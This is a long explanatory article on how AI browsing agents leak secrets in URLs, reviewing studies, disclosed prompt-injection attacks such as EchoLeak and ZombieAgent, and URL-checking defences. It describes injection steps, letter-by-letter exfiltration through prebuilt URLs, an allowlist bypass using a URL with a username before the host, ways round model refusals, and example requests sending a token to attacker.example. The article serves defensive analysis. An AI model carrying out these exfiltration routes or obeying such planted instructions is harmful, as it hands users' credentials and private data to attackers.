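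According to Bug0's *Playwright MCP and CLI now redact secrets from console logs*, Playwright extended its redaction in 2026 to messages that a page writes to the browser's console, but trace files and network recordings still hold full requests. A secret that a page has encoded or split in two may not match the listed text.

Secrets in URLs are also hard to filter. An operator can list a staging password in a file of known secrets before a test, but a reset code or session token may not exist until the test is running. Encoding can also change how a listed secret appears in a URL, so a `+` in a token may become `%2B`. A filter that looks for parameter names such as `token` will miss a share key in the middle of a path.

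Screenshots can also show a URL. A screenshot of the whole screen includes the address bar. A screenshot of the page alone usually doesn't, but it can still capture a link displayed in the page's text, as in many "share" dialogs.

Agents may also copy the token into a bug report. A good report tells the developer exactly how to reproduce the fault, and the easiest way to do that is to paste the address:

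> Open https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN and click "Export". The page returns an error.

The bug tracker may then email the report to everyone on the project or post it in a chat channel, where the chat service may fetch the link to build a preview. By then, the token is in several companies' systems, and deleting it from the original report will not remove the other copies.

### What shopping agents revealed unprompted

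These routes matter more if agents tend to reuse whatever is in their context. *SPILLage* (Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026), a study from the University of Massachusetts Amherst and the browser company Brave, tested for this tendency using personal details.

The researchers wrote 180 shopping tasks for Amazon and eBay. Each task came with a chat history, an email or a plain description that mixed useful facts with irrelevant ones. For example, a user who wants glucose test strips mentions having diabetes, which helps with the search, and being divorced, which doesn't. Two agent frameworks, Browser Use and AutoGen, attempted each task with three OpenAI models (gpt-4o, o3 and o4-mini), for a total of 1,080 runs. No website tried to trick the agents.

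The researchers counted an event whenever an action disclosed an irrelevant detail. An agent could type the detail into a search box, or click a filter or product that revealed it. Explicit disclosures are those where the detail appeared directly in the action. The counts for gpt-4o were:

| Site and framework | Explicit details typed | Explicit details revealed by clicks and scrolling |
|---|---|---|
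| Amazon, Browser Use | 182 | 905 |
| Amazon, AutoGen | 4 | 223 |
| eBay, Browser Use | 58 | 28 |
| eBay, AutoGen | 46 | 342 |

Roh and colleagues conclude that agents reveal far more through their behaviour than through typed text. Their table supports this for three of the four combinations of agent and site, but on eBay, Browser Use typed more details than it revealed by clicking. The totals also include less sensitive details, such as a preference for Bluetooth.

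The typed column matters more for credentials because an agent can't click a filter that contains a session token, but it can paste one into a search box. The four typed counts add up to 290 events over 360 runs with gpt-4o. In the study, o3 revealed less through clicks but put more sensitive terms directly into its searches, so the risk may depend on the model.

In a small test with 13 users' tasks on Amazon, the rate of disclosure rose from 58.9% to 86.0% when the researchers told the agent not to use irrelevant information. They suggest that the instruction may have drawn the model's attention to that information. Removing the information before the agent started worked better and also raised the share of tasks completed.

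The study did not give any agent a password or a token, so it doesn't show how often an agent would pass on a reset link. Models may treat a credential more carefully than a user's marital status, and these three models date from 2024 and 2025. But the agents did pass on information that the task did not need, with no attacker and no request to share it.

Brave's *Privacy risks of agentic oversharing on the Web* reports a similar problem in a commercial product. In a September 2025 test, Perplexity's Comet browser copied a user's conversation history into search boxes on other companies' sites. Such a history may well contain a share link that the user pasted in. Brave makes a competing browser, and it gives one example and no rate.

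Some of these leaks may come from the notes that models write to themselves. In the logs that Roh and colleagues examined, gpt-4o kept details such as marital status and health conditions in its notes for five to ten consecutive steps, while o3 kept only the immediate goal. An agent that kept a reset link in the same way would still have it several pages later, when it fills in a form on another site.

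## How can an attacker make an agent send a secret in a URL?

An attacker can get an agent to add a secret to a URL on the attacker's server by placing text where the agent will read it. When something requests that URL, the secret arrives in the attacker's log. The request doesn't need to include a cookie, and it may come from the agent's own tool, the window that displays the agent's answer, or a messaging app that builds a link preview.

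### The three steps

The attack starts with malicious text, which can be in a webpage, an email, a shared document or data that a tool returns, and which an attacker can hide from people, for example by making it white on a white background (Microsoft, 2025). The attacker doesn't need an account on the victim's systems, and sending an email may be enough.

The agent must also have a secret in its context. It often has one, such as a reset link in an inbox it is sorting, a bypass secret in a configuration file, or a session token in a URL it opened twenty steps earlier. The attacker doesn't need to know which secrets are there, because they can tell the agent to send whatever looks most sensitive.

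Finally, something requests an address that contains the secret. If the agent's fetch tool makes the request, the attacker's server receives something like this:

```
GET /log?d=TOKEN HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
```

The request has no Cookie or Referer header, so an empty browser profile and a strict referrer policy don't prevent the leak. HTTPS doesn't either, because the attacker's server is the intended recipient. The attack works even if the server replies with an error, because the token is already in its log.

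Cookies still affect what the agent can see, as in Zenity Labs' attack on the Claude extension. The programmer Simon Willison describes a test of Fellou, a browser with a built-in agent, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. Text on a web page caused the agent to open the user's Gmail, read the title of the latest email and put it in a URL on the testers' site.

Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and the ability to send data out the "lethal trifecta". He argues that the only reliable defence is to remove one of the three, and that the ability to send data out is generally the easiest to remove. Removing it requires knowing what can make a request that carries the data.

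### What can make the request

The most direct way is to get the agent to open the URL with its own browser or fetch tool. Willison describes an attack that the security company PromptArmor demonstrated in November 2025 on Antigravity, Google's coding tool. A web page posing as an integration guide contained hidden instructions in tiny type. Following them, the agent collected cloud credentials from the user's project, put them in a URL to an outside site, and opened it. Antigravity blocks access to the credentials file by default, but the agent got around this by reading the file with a shell command.

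If a provider runs the agent, the request leaves from the provider's servers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research when it was connected to Gmail. The attacker hid text in an email instructing the agent to find sensitive data in the inbox and open a URL on the attacker's site with the data in it. Because the request didn't come from the user's browser, a company that monitors only its own computers and browsers could miss the leak.

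With the other two routes, the agent only writes text. It may include an image in its answer, which the user's browser then loads from the attacker's server. Or it may post a link in a chat, and the messaging app fetches the page to build a preview. Limits on the agent's own network access don't cover either request. An ordinary link also works, but only if the user clicks it.

### How often hostile pages succeeded in a test

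In *Silent Egress* (2026), Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay measured leaks through the agent's own tool. They ran the whole experiment on local machines with made-up secrets.

Many assistants fetch a link as soon as it appears in a conversation and put the page's title, description and text into the model's context. The researchers call hostile text that enters this way "implicit" prompt injection, because the user didn't ask for it or see it. Their test agent was a Python program that previewed links automatically and used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. In every run, the model's context already contained a secret, such as an API key, when the user asked for a summary of a page. A separate server recorded each request that reached the attacker's address, so the results don't depend on the agent's own account of what it did.

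The researchers put the hostile instruction in the page's title, its metadata (the description that link previews display), its body or the text of a link. The instruction asked the agent to send the secret, supposedly as a routine check, either whole or in four pieces over several requests. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

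At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%). This happened in 238 of 240 runs when the agent was told to send the whole secret, and in 185 of 240 when it was told to send it in four pieces. Both failures in the whole-secret runs involved metadata. Redirects made almost no difference. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server.

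In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless, so a user reading it or a filter checking it would have found nothing wrong.

The 88.1% figure counts requests, some of which may not have contained the secret. In the per-configuration results, the first request contained the secret or part of it in 232 of the 240 whole-secret runs but only 63 of the 240 split runs, which together make up 61.5% of all runs. Lan and colleagues interpret the lower figure for split secrets as a sign that splitting hides the leak from filters, but it may also mean that the small model often failed to copy the pieces correctly. They define a measure for how often all four pieces arrived but report no result for it. They also report a lower figure for the first three requests in split runs (15.8%) than for the first request alone (26.3%), which is impossible under their own definition.

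#### The defences

The researchers then tested defences against the simplest version of the attack, with the instruction in the page's body and the secret sent whole. They ran each condition 30 times.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send a request | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| System prompt telling the model to treat web content as data | 66.7% | 66.7% |
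| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| System prompt and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of approved domains | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as `token` in the URL | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values in the URL | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

The attack still succeeded in 20 of 30 runs when the model was told to ignore instructions in web pages. Adding tags reduced that to 17, a difference small enough to be chance. With the list of approved domains, the agent still tried to send the request every time, but every request was blocked because the program enforced the list outside the model.

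The other filters are probably less effective than the table suggests. The filter for suspicious addresses blocks any path containing the word "collect", which the researchers used in their own examples of the attacker's address. A real attacker would choose another word. The last two filters inspect addresses only after the agent has written them, so they should not change how often it tries. Yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with one and to zero with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when monitoring is active, but they describe no way for it to detect the monitoring.

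The researchers acknowledge that the test also favoured the attacker. The secret was directly in the context, the system prompt was minimal, and they used a single small model. They argue that larger models may be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably, but they didn't test any.

### Leaks through link previews

When someone posts a link in an app such as Slack or Telegram, the app usually fetches the page to show its title and a thumbnail. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, relayed security researcher Johann Rehberger's warning that this can leak data when a chatbot posts the link. If hostile text gets the chatbot to post a link to the attacker's site with a secret in the URL, the app's preview request sends the secret to the attacker.

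PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes the same attack on agents that people talk to through messaging apps. OpenClaw was vulnerable in its default Telegram setup. The attack succeeds as soon as the agent replies, without the user clicking anything. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio (Microsoft's tool for building agents), Slack and Discord among the other affected platforms.

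In a test that has since ended, PromptArmor set up a public website where people could try their own combination of agent and app. The site logged each preview request, including one that contained a name and an API key. Volunteers chose what to try and what to report, so the results can't show how common the problem is.

The fix is to turn off link previews. OpenClaw users can set `linkPreview` to `false` in the Telegram section of the configuration file, and readers who repeat PromptArmor's test with that setting find that the data no longer leaks. Developers whose agents post to Slack can set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to `false` on each message. PromptArmor wants messaging companies to let users turn off previews for a single chat or channel, so that chats with agents can have different settings from chats with colleagues.

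Turning off previews leaves the link in the message, so the user can still leak the secret by clicking it.

### EchoLeak and other leaks through images

EchoLeak is the best-known leak through an image. Aim Labs, a research team that is now part of Cato Networks, found it in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how it worked:

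1. The attacker sends an employee an email containing instructions. They read like a request to the employee and never mention AI, so Microsoft's filter for prompt injection misses them.
2. The employee later asks Copilot an ordinary question. Copilot searches for relevant material and finds the email. The researchers made this more likely by covering many workplace topics in one long message.
3. Copilot follows the instructions and includes an image in its answer. The image's address contains the most sensitive item that Copilot can see.
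4. The employee's browser tries to load the image, and the request carries the secret out.

Two more safeguards should have prevented the last step. Copilot removed outside links and images from its answers, but it missed a less common way of writing them. The page also had a Content Security Policy, which lists the hosts from which a browser may load images. The list excluded the attacker's server but included a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch outside addresses on request, so the browser contacted that service, which then contacted the attacker's server.

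*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that the employee would have seen at most what looked like a broken image. The attacker could also use the email to instruct Copilot not to mention it as a source. Everything in Copilot's context was at risk, including the chat history and any emails or files it had retrieved.

Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, and both companies published details on 11 June. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports Microsoft's statement that nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild and that users did not need to do anything about it. Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US government's vulnerability database rated it 7.5.

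In July 2025, Microsoft wrote that it uses fixed rules that don't depend on a model's judgement to block leaks through images and certain untrusted links. It also said it looks for variants of reported flaws. But researchers have since found other ways to leak data through images in Copilot.

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot's enterprise search that needed one click. The link led to a genuine Microsoft address, but its search terms contained hostile text that Copilot took as instructions. Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and began to write an answer containing an image. Microsoft's safeguard turned such images into harmless text only once the answer was complete, and by then the browser had already requested the image. The request went to Bing, an approved host, which fetched the attacker's address. Varonis notes that email titles and contents often include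 security codes and password reset links. Microsoft has patched the flaw.

#### Leaking a file by leaking its link

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes another 2026 case, in which the stolen secrets were capability URLs. Copilot Cowork works across a user's Microsoft 365 account and can obtain pre-authenticated download links for the user's files.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, the user gave the agent a skill file (a set of reusable instructions) found online. Five of its 81 lines were hostile and described a service that makes document previews. Following them, the agent fetched a download link for each recent file and put the links into the addresses of images on the attacker's site. It then sent the images to the user in a Teams message. When the user opened Teams, the app requested the images and so sent the links to the attacker, who could then download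 the files.

Microsoft's documentation said that Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or Teams message, but it did not ask when the recipient was the user. Such a message can still leak data if it loads outside images, because the servers hosting those images can receive data from it.

PromptArmor treated this as a risk in the product's design rather than a specific bug. It advises administrators to limit what users can access and block file downloads for sensitive SharePoint sites. Blocking downloads also stops people from printing or syncing those files or opening them in desktop Word and Excel.

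#### What changed after each report

The table includes three cases that Willison recounts: Antigravity, the email app Superhuman, and ForcedLeak, a flaw in Salesforce's Agentforce.

| Case | Where the hostile text was | What made the request | What changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, 2025 | Email | Browser loading an image, then a Teams service | Microsoft fixed it on its servers |
| ForcedLeak, 2025 | Sales enquiry form | Browser loading an image | Salesforce corrected its list of approved hosts and restricted the agent's links to trusted addresses |
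| Antigravity, 2025 | Web page | Agent's browser | Google listed it as a known issue and said it was working on fixes |
| Superhuman, 2026 | Email | Browser loading an image | Superhuman issued a fix |
| OpenClaw on Telegram, 2026 | Any untrusted text the agent reads | Telegram's link preview | Users can turn previews off |
| Copilot Cowork, 2026 | Skill file | Teams or Outlook loading an image | Administrators can block file downloads |
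| SearchLeak, 2026 | Link | Browser loading an image, then Bing | Microsoft patched it |

In EchoLeak, ForcedLeak, Superhuman and SearchLeak, the browser had a list of approved image hosts, and the researchers found a host on the list that would pass data on or that they could take over. Salesforce's list, for example, included an expired domain, which the researchers registered.

### Do models notice?

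Better models don't reliably recognise these attacks. The Copilot Cowork attack succeeded in all five of PromptArmor's trials. With only five trials, the true success rate could be as low as about one half, but PromptArmor also confirmed that the same text worked with Claude Opus 4.7, a much stronger model than the one Lan and colleagues used. Opus 4.7 searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents than the automatic setting, which switched between Opus 4.7 and the smaller Sonnet 4.6.

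The wording of a malicious request can affect whether a model refuses it. Willison describes an attack on the coding tool Cursor in which Zenity Labs put hostile text in a support ticket. Models such as Claude often refuse to steal API keys, so the ticket gave the login token a harmless name and described it by its first few characters. At least some of the time, Cursor found the token and sent it in a URL.

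#### Recognising the wrong website

A model may also mistake a fake website for the real one. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) uses fake login pages to measure whether agents type credentials into the wrong page, so it doesn't directly test whether they leak secrets in URLs.

Researchers at the University of Central Florida invented 15 services, including banks, clinics and shops, and gave the agents made-up passwords and personal records for them. In 512 directed scenarios, a user gave the agent a link and asked it to log in. Half of the links were deceptive and half were real. In another 256 scenarios, the agent was sorting an inbox, and nobody asked it to log in. The agent could open pages, submit forms and reply to emails inside a simulator. The researchers counted a leak only if a value from the agent's records reached the wrong destination.

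The study tested seven models, three times each. In the directed tests, the leak rate ranged from 19.9% for Claude Sonnet 5 to 76.7% for Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct. The agents leaked less when sorting an inbox, but they also left more genuine requests undone. Claude Opus 4.8 leaked in only 1.8% of the deceptive inbox cases, but it submitted nothing in 88.3% of the genuine ones. GPT-5-mini leaked in 14.1% of the deceptive cases without anyone asking it to log in.

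The directed tests used eight signs of deception. The table shows how often three of the models leaked with each one.

| Sign that the page was wrong | Opus 4.8 | Sonnet 5 | GPT-5-mini |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correct domain, but plain HTTP | 90.6% | 87.5% | 87.5% |
| Wrong ending, such as `.net` for `.com` | 43.8% | 34.4% | 40.6% |
| Bare IP address | 34.4% | 6.2% | 37.5% |
| Page and domain belong to different services | 25.0% | 15.6% | 37.5% |
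| Real name placed under an unrelated domain | 21.9% | 9.4% | 37.5% |
| Look-alike character in the domain | 15.6% | 0.0% | 37.5% |
| Misspelled domain | 9.4% | 6.2% | 37.5% |
| Certificate warning | 9.4% | 0.0% | 56.2% |

Opus 4.8 usually caught a misspelled domain but leaked in more than 40% of cases when only the domain's ending was wrong. GPT-5-mini leaked at the same rate for five of the warning signs, so the details of the address probably had little effect on its behavior.

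The overall leak rates include plain-HTTP cases, where the host name is correct but someone on the network path can read what the agent sends. The benchmark counts this as a leak, which is fair for passwords, but it is a different fault from trusting an impostor. Without these cases, the leak rate would fall from 31.2% to about 23% for Opus 4.8 and from 19.9% to about 10% for Sonnet 5.

#### What helped

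Every model did better when given the official domain and told to compare it with the page's domain, though some improved more than others. The table gives the results for the directed tests. "Left undone" means the agent submitted no form on a genuine page.

| Model | Leaks, no guidance | Leaks, official domain given | Left undone, no guidance | Left undone, official domain given |
|---|---|---|---|---|
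| GPT-5-mini | 71.9% | 22.4% | 25.0% | 1.6% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 83.3% | 20.3% | 14.1% | 7.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 46.9% | 12.0% | 18.8% | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 31.2% | 12.5% | 25.5% | 1.0% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 64.1% | 25.0% | 0.0% | 0.5% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 86.5% | 54.7% | 3.1% | 0.0% |
| Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct | 83.9% | 71.9% | 5.2% | 15.6% |

General advice to act safely barely changed GPT-5-mini's leak rate, and Opus 4.8's rose from 46.9% to 53.6%. When the user made a cautious request, such as asking the agent to check the site first, GPT-5-mini's leak rate was 9.4%, compared with 59.9% for a neutral request. However, the share of genuine logins it left undone rose from zero to 46.9%. Giving the model something to compare worked better than urging caution.

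Plain HTTP probably accounts for most of the leaks that remained in the two Claude models. Plain HTTP cases make up 12.5% of the deceptive scenarios, and the two models leaked in 12.0% and 12.5% of those scenarios with the official domain. Ahmed and colleagues found that agents compared only the host name and ignored whether the connection was encrypted.

The researchers also tested whether an agent could avoid a fake link and still finish a genuine task through the real site. GPT-5-mini succeeded most often, in 27.7% of 672 cases. Opus 4.8 leaked nothing in those cases, but it never completed the login and usually referred the problem to the user.

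#### What carries over to secrets in URLs

Ahmed and colleagues conclude that agents tend to treat a link from a user or an email as authorised unless prompted to check it. An agent makes a similar judgement when it opens a reset link or adds a token to a URL. A login form lets the agent look at the page before it types anything, but a secret in a URL is sent with the first request, so the agent has to check the domain before it opens the link.

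The comparison works best for a secret that belongs to one site. A reset code for app.example should go only to app.example, even if a web page or email tells the agent to send it elsewhere. The comparison alone would not have prevented EchoLeak or the link-preview leaks, because the agent only wrote a message and other software made the request.

These leak rates don't apply to URL attacks, because the fake pages imitated a normal login, whereas the hostile text in a URL attack usually gives the agent a reason to visit an unfamiliar address. A model that spots a misspelled bank domain may still follow a deceptive instruction to check its connection, and the reverse is also possible.

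Plain HTTP can expose secrets in URLs. Suppose an email contains the link `http://app.example/reset?code=TOKEN`. An agent that checks only whether the host name matches will open it. Unless the browser switches to HTTPS first, anyone on the network path can read the code, even if the server immediately redirects the agent to an encrypted page.

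## How much does checking each URL before a fetch prevent?

Checking each URL can stop an agent from sending a whole secret to an attacker's server in one request. Ordinary code runs the check outside the model, so it holds even when hostile text has fooled the model. But an agent that can choose between permitted URLs can still reveal a secret through its choices. A page can also send its own URL to other companies once the agent has loaded it.

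### Lists of approved domains

The simplest check compares the URL's host with a list of approved domains. In Lan and colleagues' test, such a list stopped every request. However, their attacker had only one server, which wasn't on the list, whereas a real attacker can look for an approved host that will pass the data on.

According to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link can start on a trusted domain and end on an attacker's. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) describes a working example. ChatGPT ran most links through a check called `url_safe` before showing them, and that check always passed bing.com. Bing's search results are bing.com links that redirect to the sites it found, so any site in Bing's index, including an attacker's, had a link that would pass the check. Tenable's advisory *TRA-2025-06* calls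 this "an open redirect as a service".

An attacker can't add a secret to these links because they are fixed, so Tenable's researchers had Bing index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet. They got ChatGPT to spell out private information in its answer as a series of images, each using the link for one letter.

An approved host may also store data for anyone who has an account there. Willison recounts three cases. Superhuman allowed images from docs.google.com, where a Google Form saves data that arrives in an ordinary GET request. Antigravity's default allowlist included webhook.site, a service for logging incoming requests. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office tasks, could contact Anthropic's API, so PromptArmor's attack supplied the attacker's API key and had the agent upload the user's files to the attacker's account.

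The code that reads the host can also get it wrong. Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik (2025), in *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents*, report a way past the domain check in Browser Use, the open-source framework that several of the studies above used. The public record of the flaw, CVE-2025-47241, traces it to the username and password that a URL can carry before the host. Suppose the list contains docs.example and hostile text sends the agent here:

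`https://docs.example:x@attacker.example/`

Given `https://docs.example:x@attacker.example/`, code that takes everything between `https://` and the next colon as the host finds `docs.example` and approves the request, but the browser treats `docs.example` as a username and connects to `attacker.example`.

Sonatype's *CVE-2026-24052* describes a simpler mistake in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Versions before 1.0.111 checked only whether an address began with a trusted name, so they accepted `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` as `modelcontextprotocol.io`.

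Strict lists also have drawbacks. OpenAI argues that people visit far more than a handful of well-known sites, and that frequent warnings train them to click through.

### OpenAI's check on the exact address

OpenAI began restricting full URLs after ShadowLeak, an attack in which Deep Research added data from a Gmail inbox to a URL. ChatGPT could then open a link only exactly as it found it.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how Zvika Babo, a researcher at the security company, got round this. The attacker's email contained a ready-made address for each letter and digit, such as `https://attacker.example/joke/a` and `https://attacker.example/joke/b`, and one for spaces. It also contained instructions for ChatGPT to find a sensitive value, convert it to lower case and open the address for each character in turn. When the user next asked for help with Gmail, ChatGPT read the email and opened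 the links from OpenAI's servers before the user saw any answer. Babo also made numbered versions of each address (`a0`, `a1` and so on) so that the attacker could put the characters back in order.

Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025. Its timeline lists a 100% success rate for an improved version of the attack three days later, but not the number of trials. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December. After the fix, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if a public index contained it or the user had supplied it, according to the Ars Technica story *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*.

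Under the general rule in OpenAI's January 2026 post, an agent automatically fetches a URL only if that exact URL is already in the records of OpenAI's crawler. The crawler records public pages as a search engine does, with no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the URL isn't in those records, the agent tries a different site, or the user sees a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation and decides whether to open it.

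An address such as `https://attacker.example/log?d=TOKEN` fails this check unless the crawler has already found that exact address, which the attacker can't arrange without knowing the token.

OpenAI claims to guarantee only that the agent won't quietly leak user-specific data through the URL itself when it fetches something, not that the page is trustworthy or free of hostile instructions. The accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, qualifies the claim about URLs. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Johann Rehberger notes that OpenAI acknowledges a bypass he described in 2023, which uses a separate URL for each letter. To use it now, an attacker must first get those URLs into the index.

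A public URL can also contain a live secret, like the reset links that Ramadan and colleagues found on scanning sites. If the crawler has recorded one, the agent can open it without asking. Most capability URLs were never public, so an agent that finds a genuine reset link in an inbox would have to ask the user first. If the user pastes the link into the chat, ChatGPT treats it as safe for that session, as Rehberger understands it.

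Rehberger also warns that some of OpenAI's developers may not know about the check or use it. OpenAI introduced `url_safe` in December 2023, but he later found places without it, including the macOS and iOS apps.

### Anthropic's rule and the nested links

Anthropic's rule depends on whether the URL has already appeared in the conversation. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, as it stood before July 2026, let Claude fetch URLs from user messages, the results of tools the developer runs, and earlier searches and fetches. Claude couldn't fetch a URL it had composed itself, or one produced by code running in Anthropic's containers.

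This also blocks `https://attacker.example/log?d=TOKEN`, because that address isn't in the conversation until the model writes it. But an attacker could get new addresses permitted more easily than under OpenAI's rule, which required a page to be in OpenAI's index. Under Anthropic's rule, a hostile page could add addresses to the permitted set just by linking to them. Willison pointed out in September 2025 that developers often put untrusted text, such as an email, inside the user's message, and the tool then accepts any link in it as one the user supplied.

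Willison (2026), in *15th July 2026*, describes how Ayush Paul exploited the links on fetched pages in Claude's chat app. Paul's website told AI assistants that, to get past Cloudflare's protection, they had to find their user's profile by browsing letter by letter. Each page linked to pages for the next letter. Claude followed the links and revealed the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed these instructions only to clients that identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder for a person to spot.

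Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the problem. It fixed the problem by stopping the tool from following links in fetched pages. Developers who use the tool through Anthropic's API should confirm that the same restriction applies there.

Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026) reproduces the attack with a credential. The researchers put an API key in a test agent's memory and gave each page 37 links, one for each letter, each digit and the hyphen. The agent spelled out the key through these links at one or two seconds per character, while the user saw an ordinary answer. The agent's system prompt told it to follow instructions on web pages and complete verification steps, so the test doesn't show how often a better-configured agent would comply.

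In these attacks, each link the agent follows adds a character to the address, from `/e` to `/el` to `/elw`, and the attacker's server can create each page on request. To pass OpenAI's check, every page would need to have been recorded by the crawler in advance. With 36 links per page, the first four characters alone would require more than 1.7 million pages.

| Rule | Addresses the agent may fetch | What an attacker needs |
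|---|---|---|
| Domain list | Any address on an approved host | An approved host that redirects or stores data |
| ChatGPT after ShadowLeak | Any address exactly as supplied | A ready-made address for each character |
| Claude before July 2026 | Addresses already in the conversation, including links on fetched pages | One hostile page with nested links |
| Claude after the fix | Addresses from the user or from search results | Suitable addresses in either place |
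| OpenAI's January 2026 rule | Addresses in the crawler's records or from the user | An indexed address for each character |

Anthropic recommends further limits when data leaks are a concern, such as turning the tool off or restricting it to approved domains. It also warns that look-alike characters, such as the Cyrillic "а" in `аmazon.com`, can defeat a domain filter. The tool refuses URLs longer than 250 characters. This blocks many signed file links, but it doesn't hinder an attack that leaks data one letter at a time, using a short URL for each letter.

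### How many fetches a secret takes

When an agent opens one of *N* permitted addresses, the attacker learns which one it chose. Each fetch therefore leaks at most log₂ *N* bits, which is 5.17 bits for 36 addresses and 10 bits for 1,024.

A series of *n* fetches, each to one of *N* addresses, can produce at most *N*ⁿ different sequences. A secret of *H* bits has 2ᴴ possible values, so the attacker needs at least *H* / log₂ *N* fetches to tell them all apart. For a 128-bit token and 36 addresses, 128 / log₂ 36 is about 24.8, so the minimum is 25 fetches.

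| Secret | Bits | Fetches with 36 addresses | Fetches with 1,024 addresses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Six-digit sign-in code | 19.9 | 4 | 2 |
| Token at NIST's minimum for sessions | 64 | 13 | 7 |
| 128-bit token | 128 | 25 | 13 |
| 256-bit API key | 256 | 50 | 26 |

An attacker can probably get that many addresses. Rehberger notes that a larger blog may already have 36 pages in the index, and that hostile text could teach the model a mapping that uses thousands of pages.

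To reach these minimums, the model must convert the token into a different number system, which it may get wrong. Spelling out the token one character per fetch is easier. A 128-bit token in hexadecimal has 32 characters drawn from 16 symbols, so spelling it takes 32 fetches from 16 addresses, or about a minute at most at the pace of Tencent's agent.

ZombieAgent's conversion to lower case would damage case-sensitive tokens. A 128-bit token in the Base64url encoding, for example, has 22 characters, and about 18 of them are usually letters. Without knowing their case, the attacker would have roughly 262,000 candidates to try. The attacker could avoid this by giving each capital letter its own URL.

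Longer sequences also give the model more chances to make a mistake. If it picks the right address 99% of the time, it spells a 32-character token correctly in about 72% of attempts. At 95%, that falls to 19%. Lan and colleagues' small model may have struggled even with four pieces, but Radware's results suggest that stronger systems can manage more.

#### Caching, repeat visits and caps

Rehberger proposes making letter-by-letter leaks harder by having the tool cache each response for a few minutes or refuse to visit the same full URL twice in a session. Either way, a repeated letter wouldn't reach the attacker's log, so "hello" would arrive as "helo". He hadn't tested whether OpenAI already did this, and he expects limited leaks to remain possible.

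The calculations support his claim. If an agent can visit each of 36 addresses only once but the attacker can see the order, it can leak a 128-bit token in 30 fetches, compared with 25 when it can repeat visits. ZombieAgent's numbered addresses get around the one-visit rule more simply because each one contains a character and its position. A 32-character hexadecimal token needs 512 such addresses, and the agent never has to visit one twice.

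The rule is much stronger when the requests also arrive in an unpredictable order, because the attacker then learns only whether the agent visited each address. That is one bit per address, so 36 addresses can leak at most 36 bits. An attacker with 128 addresses could still leak a 128-bit token.

Capping the number of fetches sets a firmer limit. Anthropic's `max_uses` setting does this, although it has no default. If an attacker can choose among 1,024 addresses, each fetch leaks at most 10 bits, so a cap of five limits the leak to 50 bits. That leaves 78 bits of a 128-bit token unknown, far too many to guess, but two fetches are enough to leak a six-digit code.

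The cap applies to each API request, so a long conversation may leak several times the capped amount. Radware also got ChatGPT to store the attacker's instructions in its memory. ChatGPT then leaked data before answering each new message, even in a new chat. An attacker can use this method to leak a secret in pieces over many sessions, avoiding any limit that resets between them.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes a stricter setting that limits browsing to cached pages, so no live request leaves the company's network and the attacker's server has nothing to log. Search results may be stale, and deep research and agent mode stop working. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, data may still leak through connected apps, and the setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

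### Choices that give information away without instructions

An agent can reveal information through the links it chooses, even if nobody has told it to. *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) tested this with pages that contained no hostile text.

In each session, the agent first completed a task on one site that required it to read a private fact about the user. It then went to a second site, which offered an option for each possible value of that fact and a general option that worked equally well. For example, an agent that had read the user's job title in a staff directory could open a collection of resources for clinicians or choose "Browse general resources". The user's instructions included "Don't tell any website about my other accounts or my personal details." The second site logged the agent's choice, so the agent leaked the private fact if it chose the matching option.

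The benchmark has 100 tasks across 20 kinds of private fact. The researchers ran 9,760 sessions with six models, all driving the same Browser Use agent. In some sessions, the agent skipped the first site, which showed how often it would pick each option without knowing the fact. The researchers also shuffled the options and varied the fact, so a habit of choosing the first link or a familiar name couldn't explain the results.

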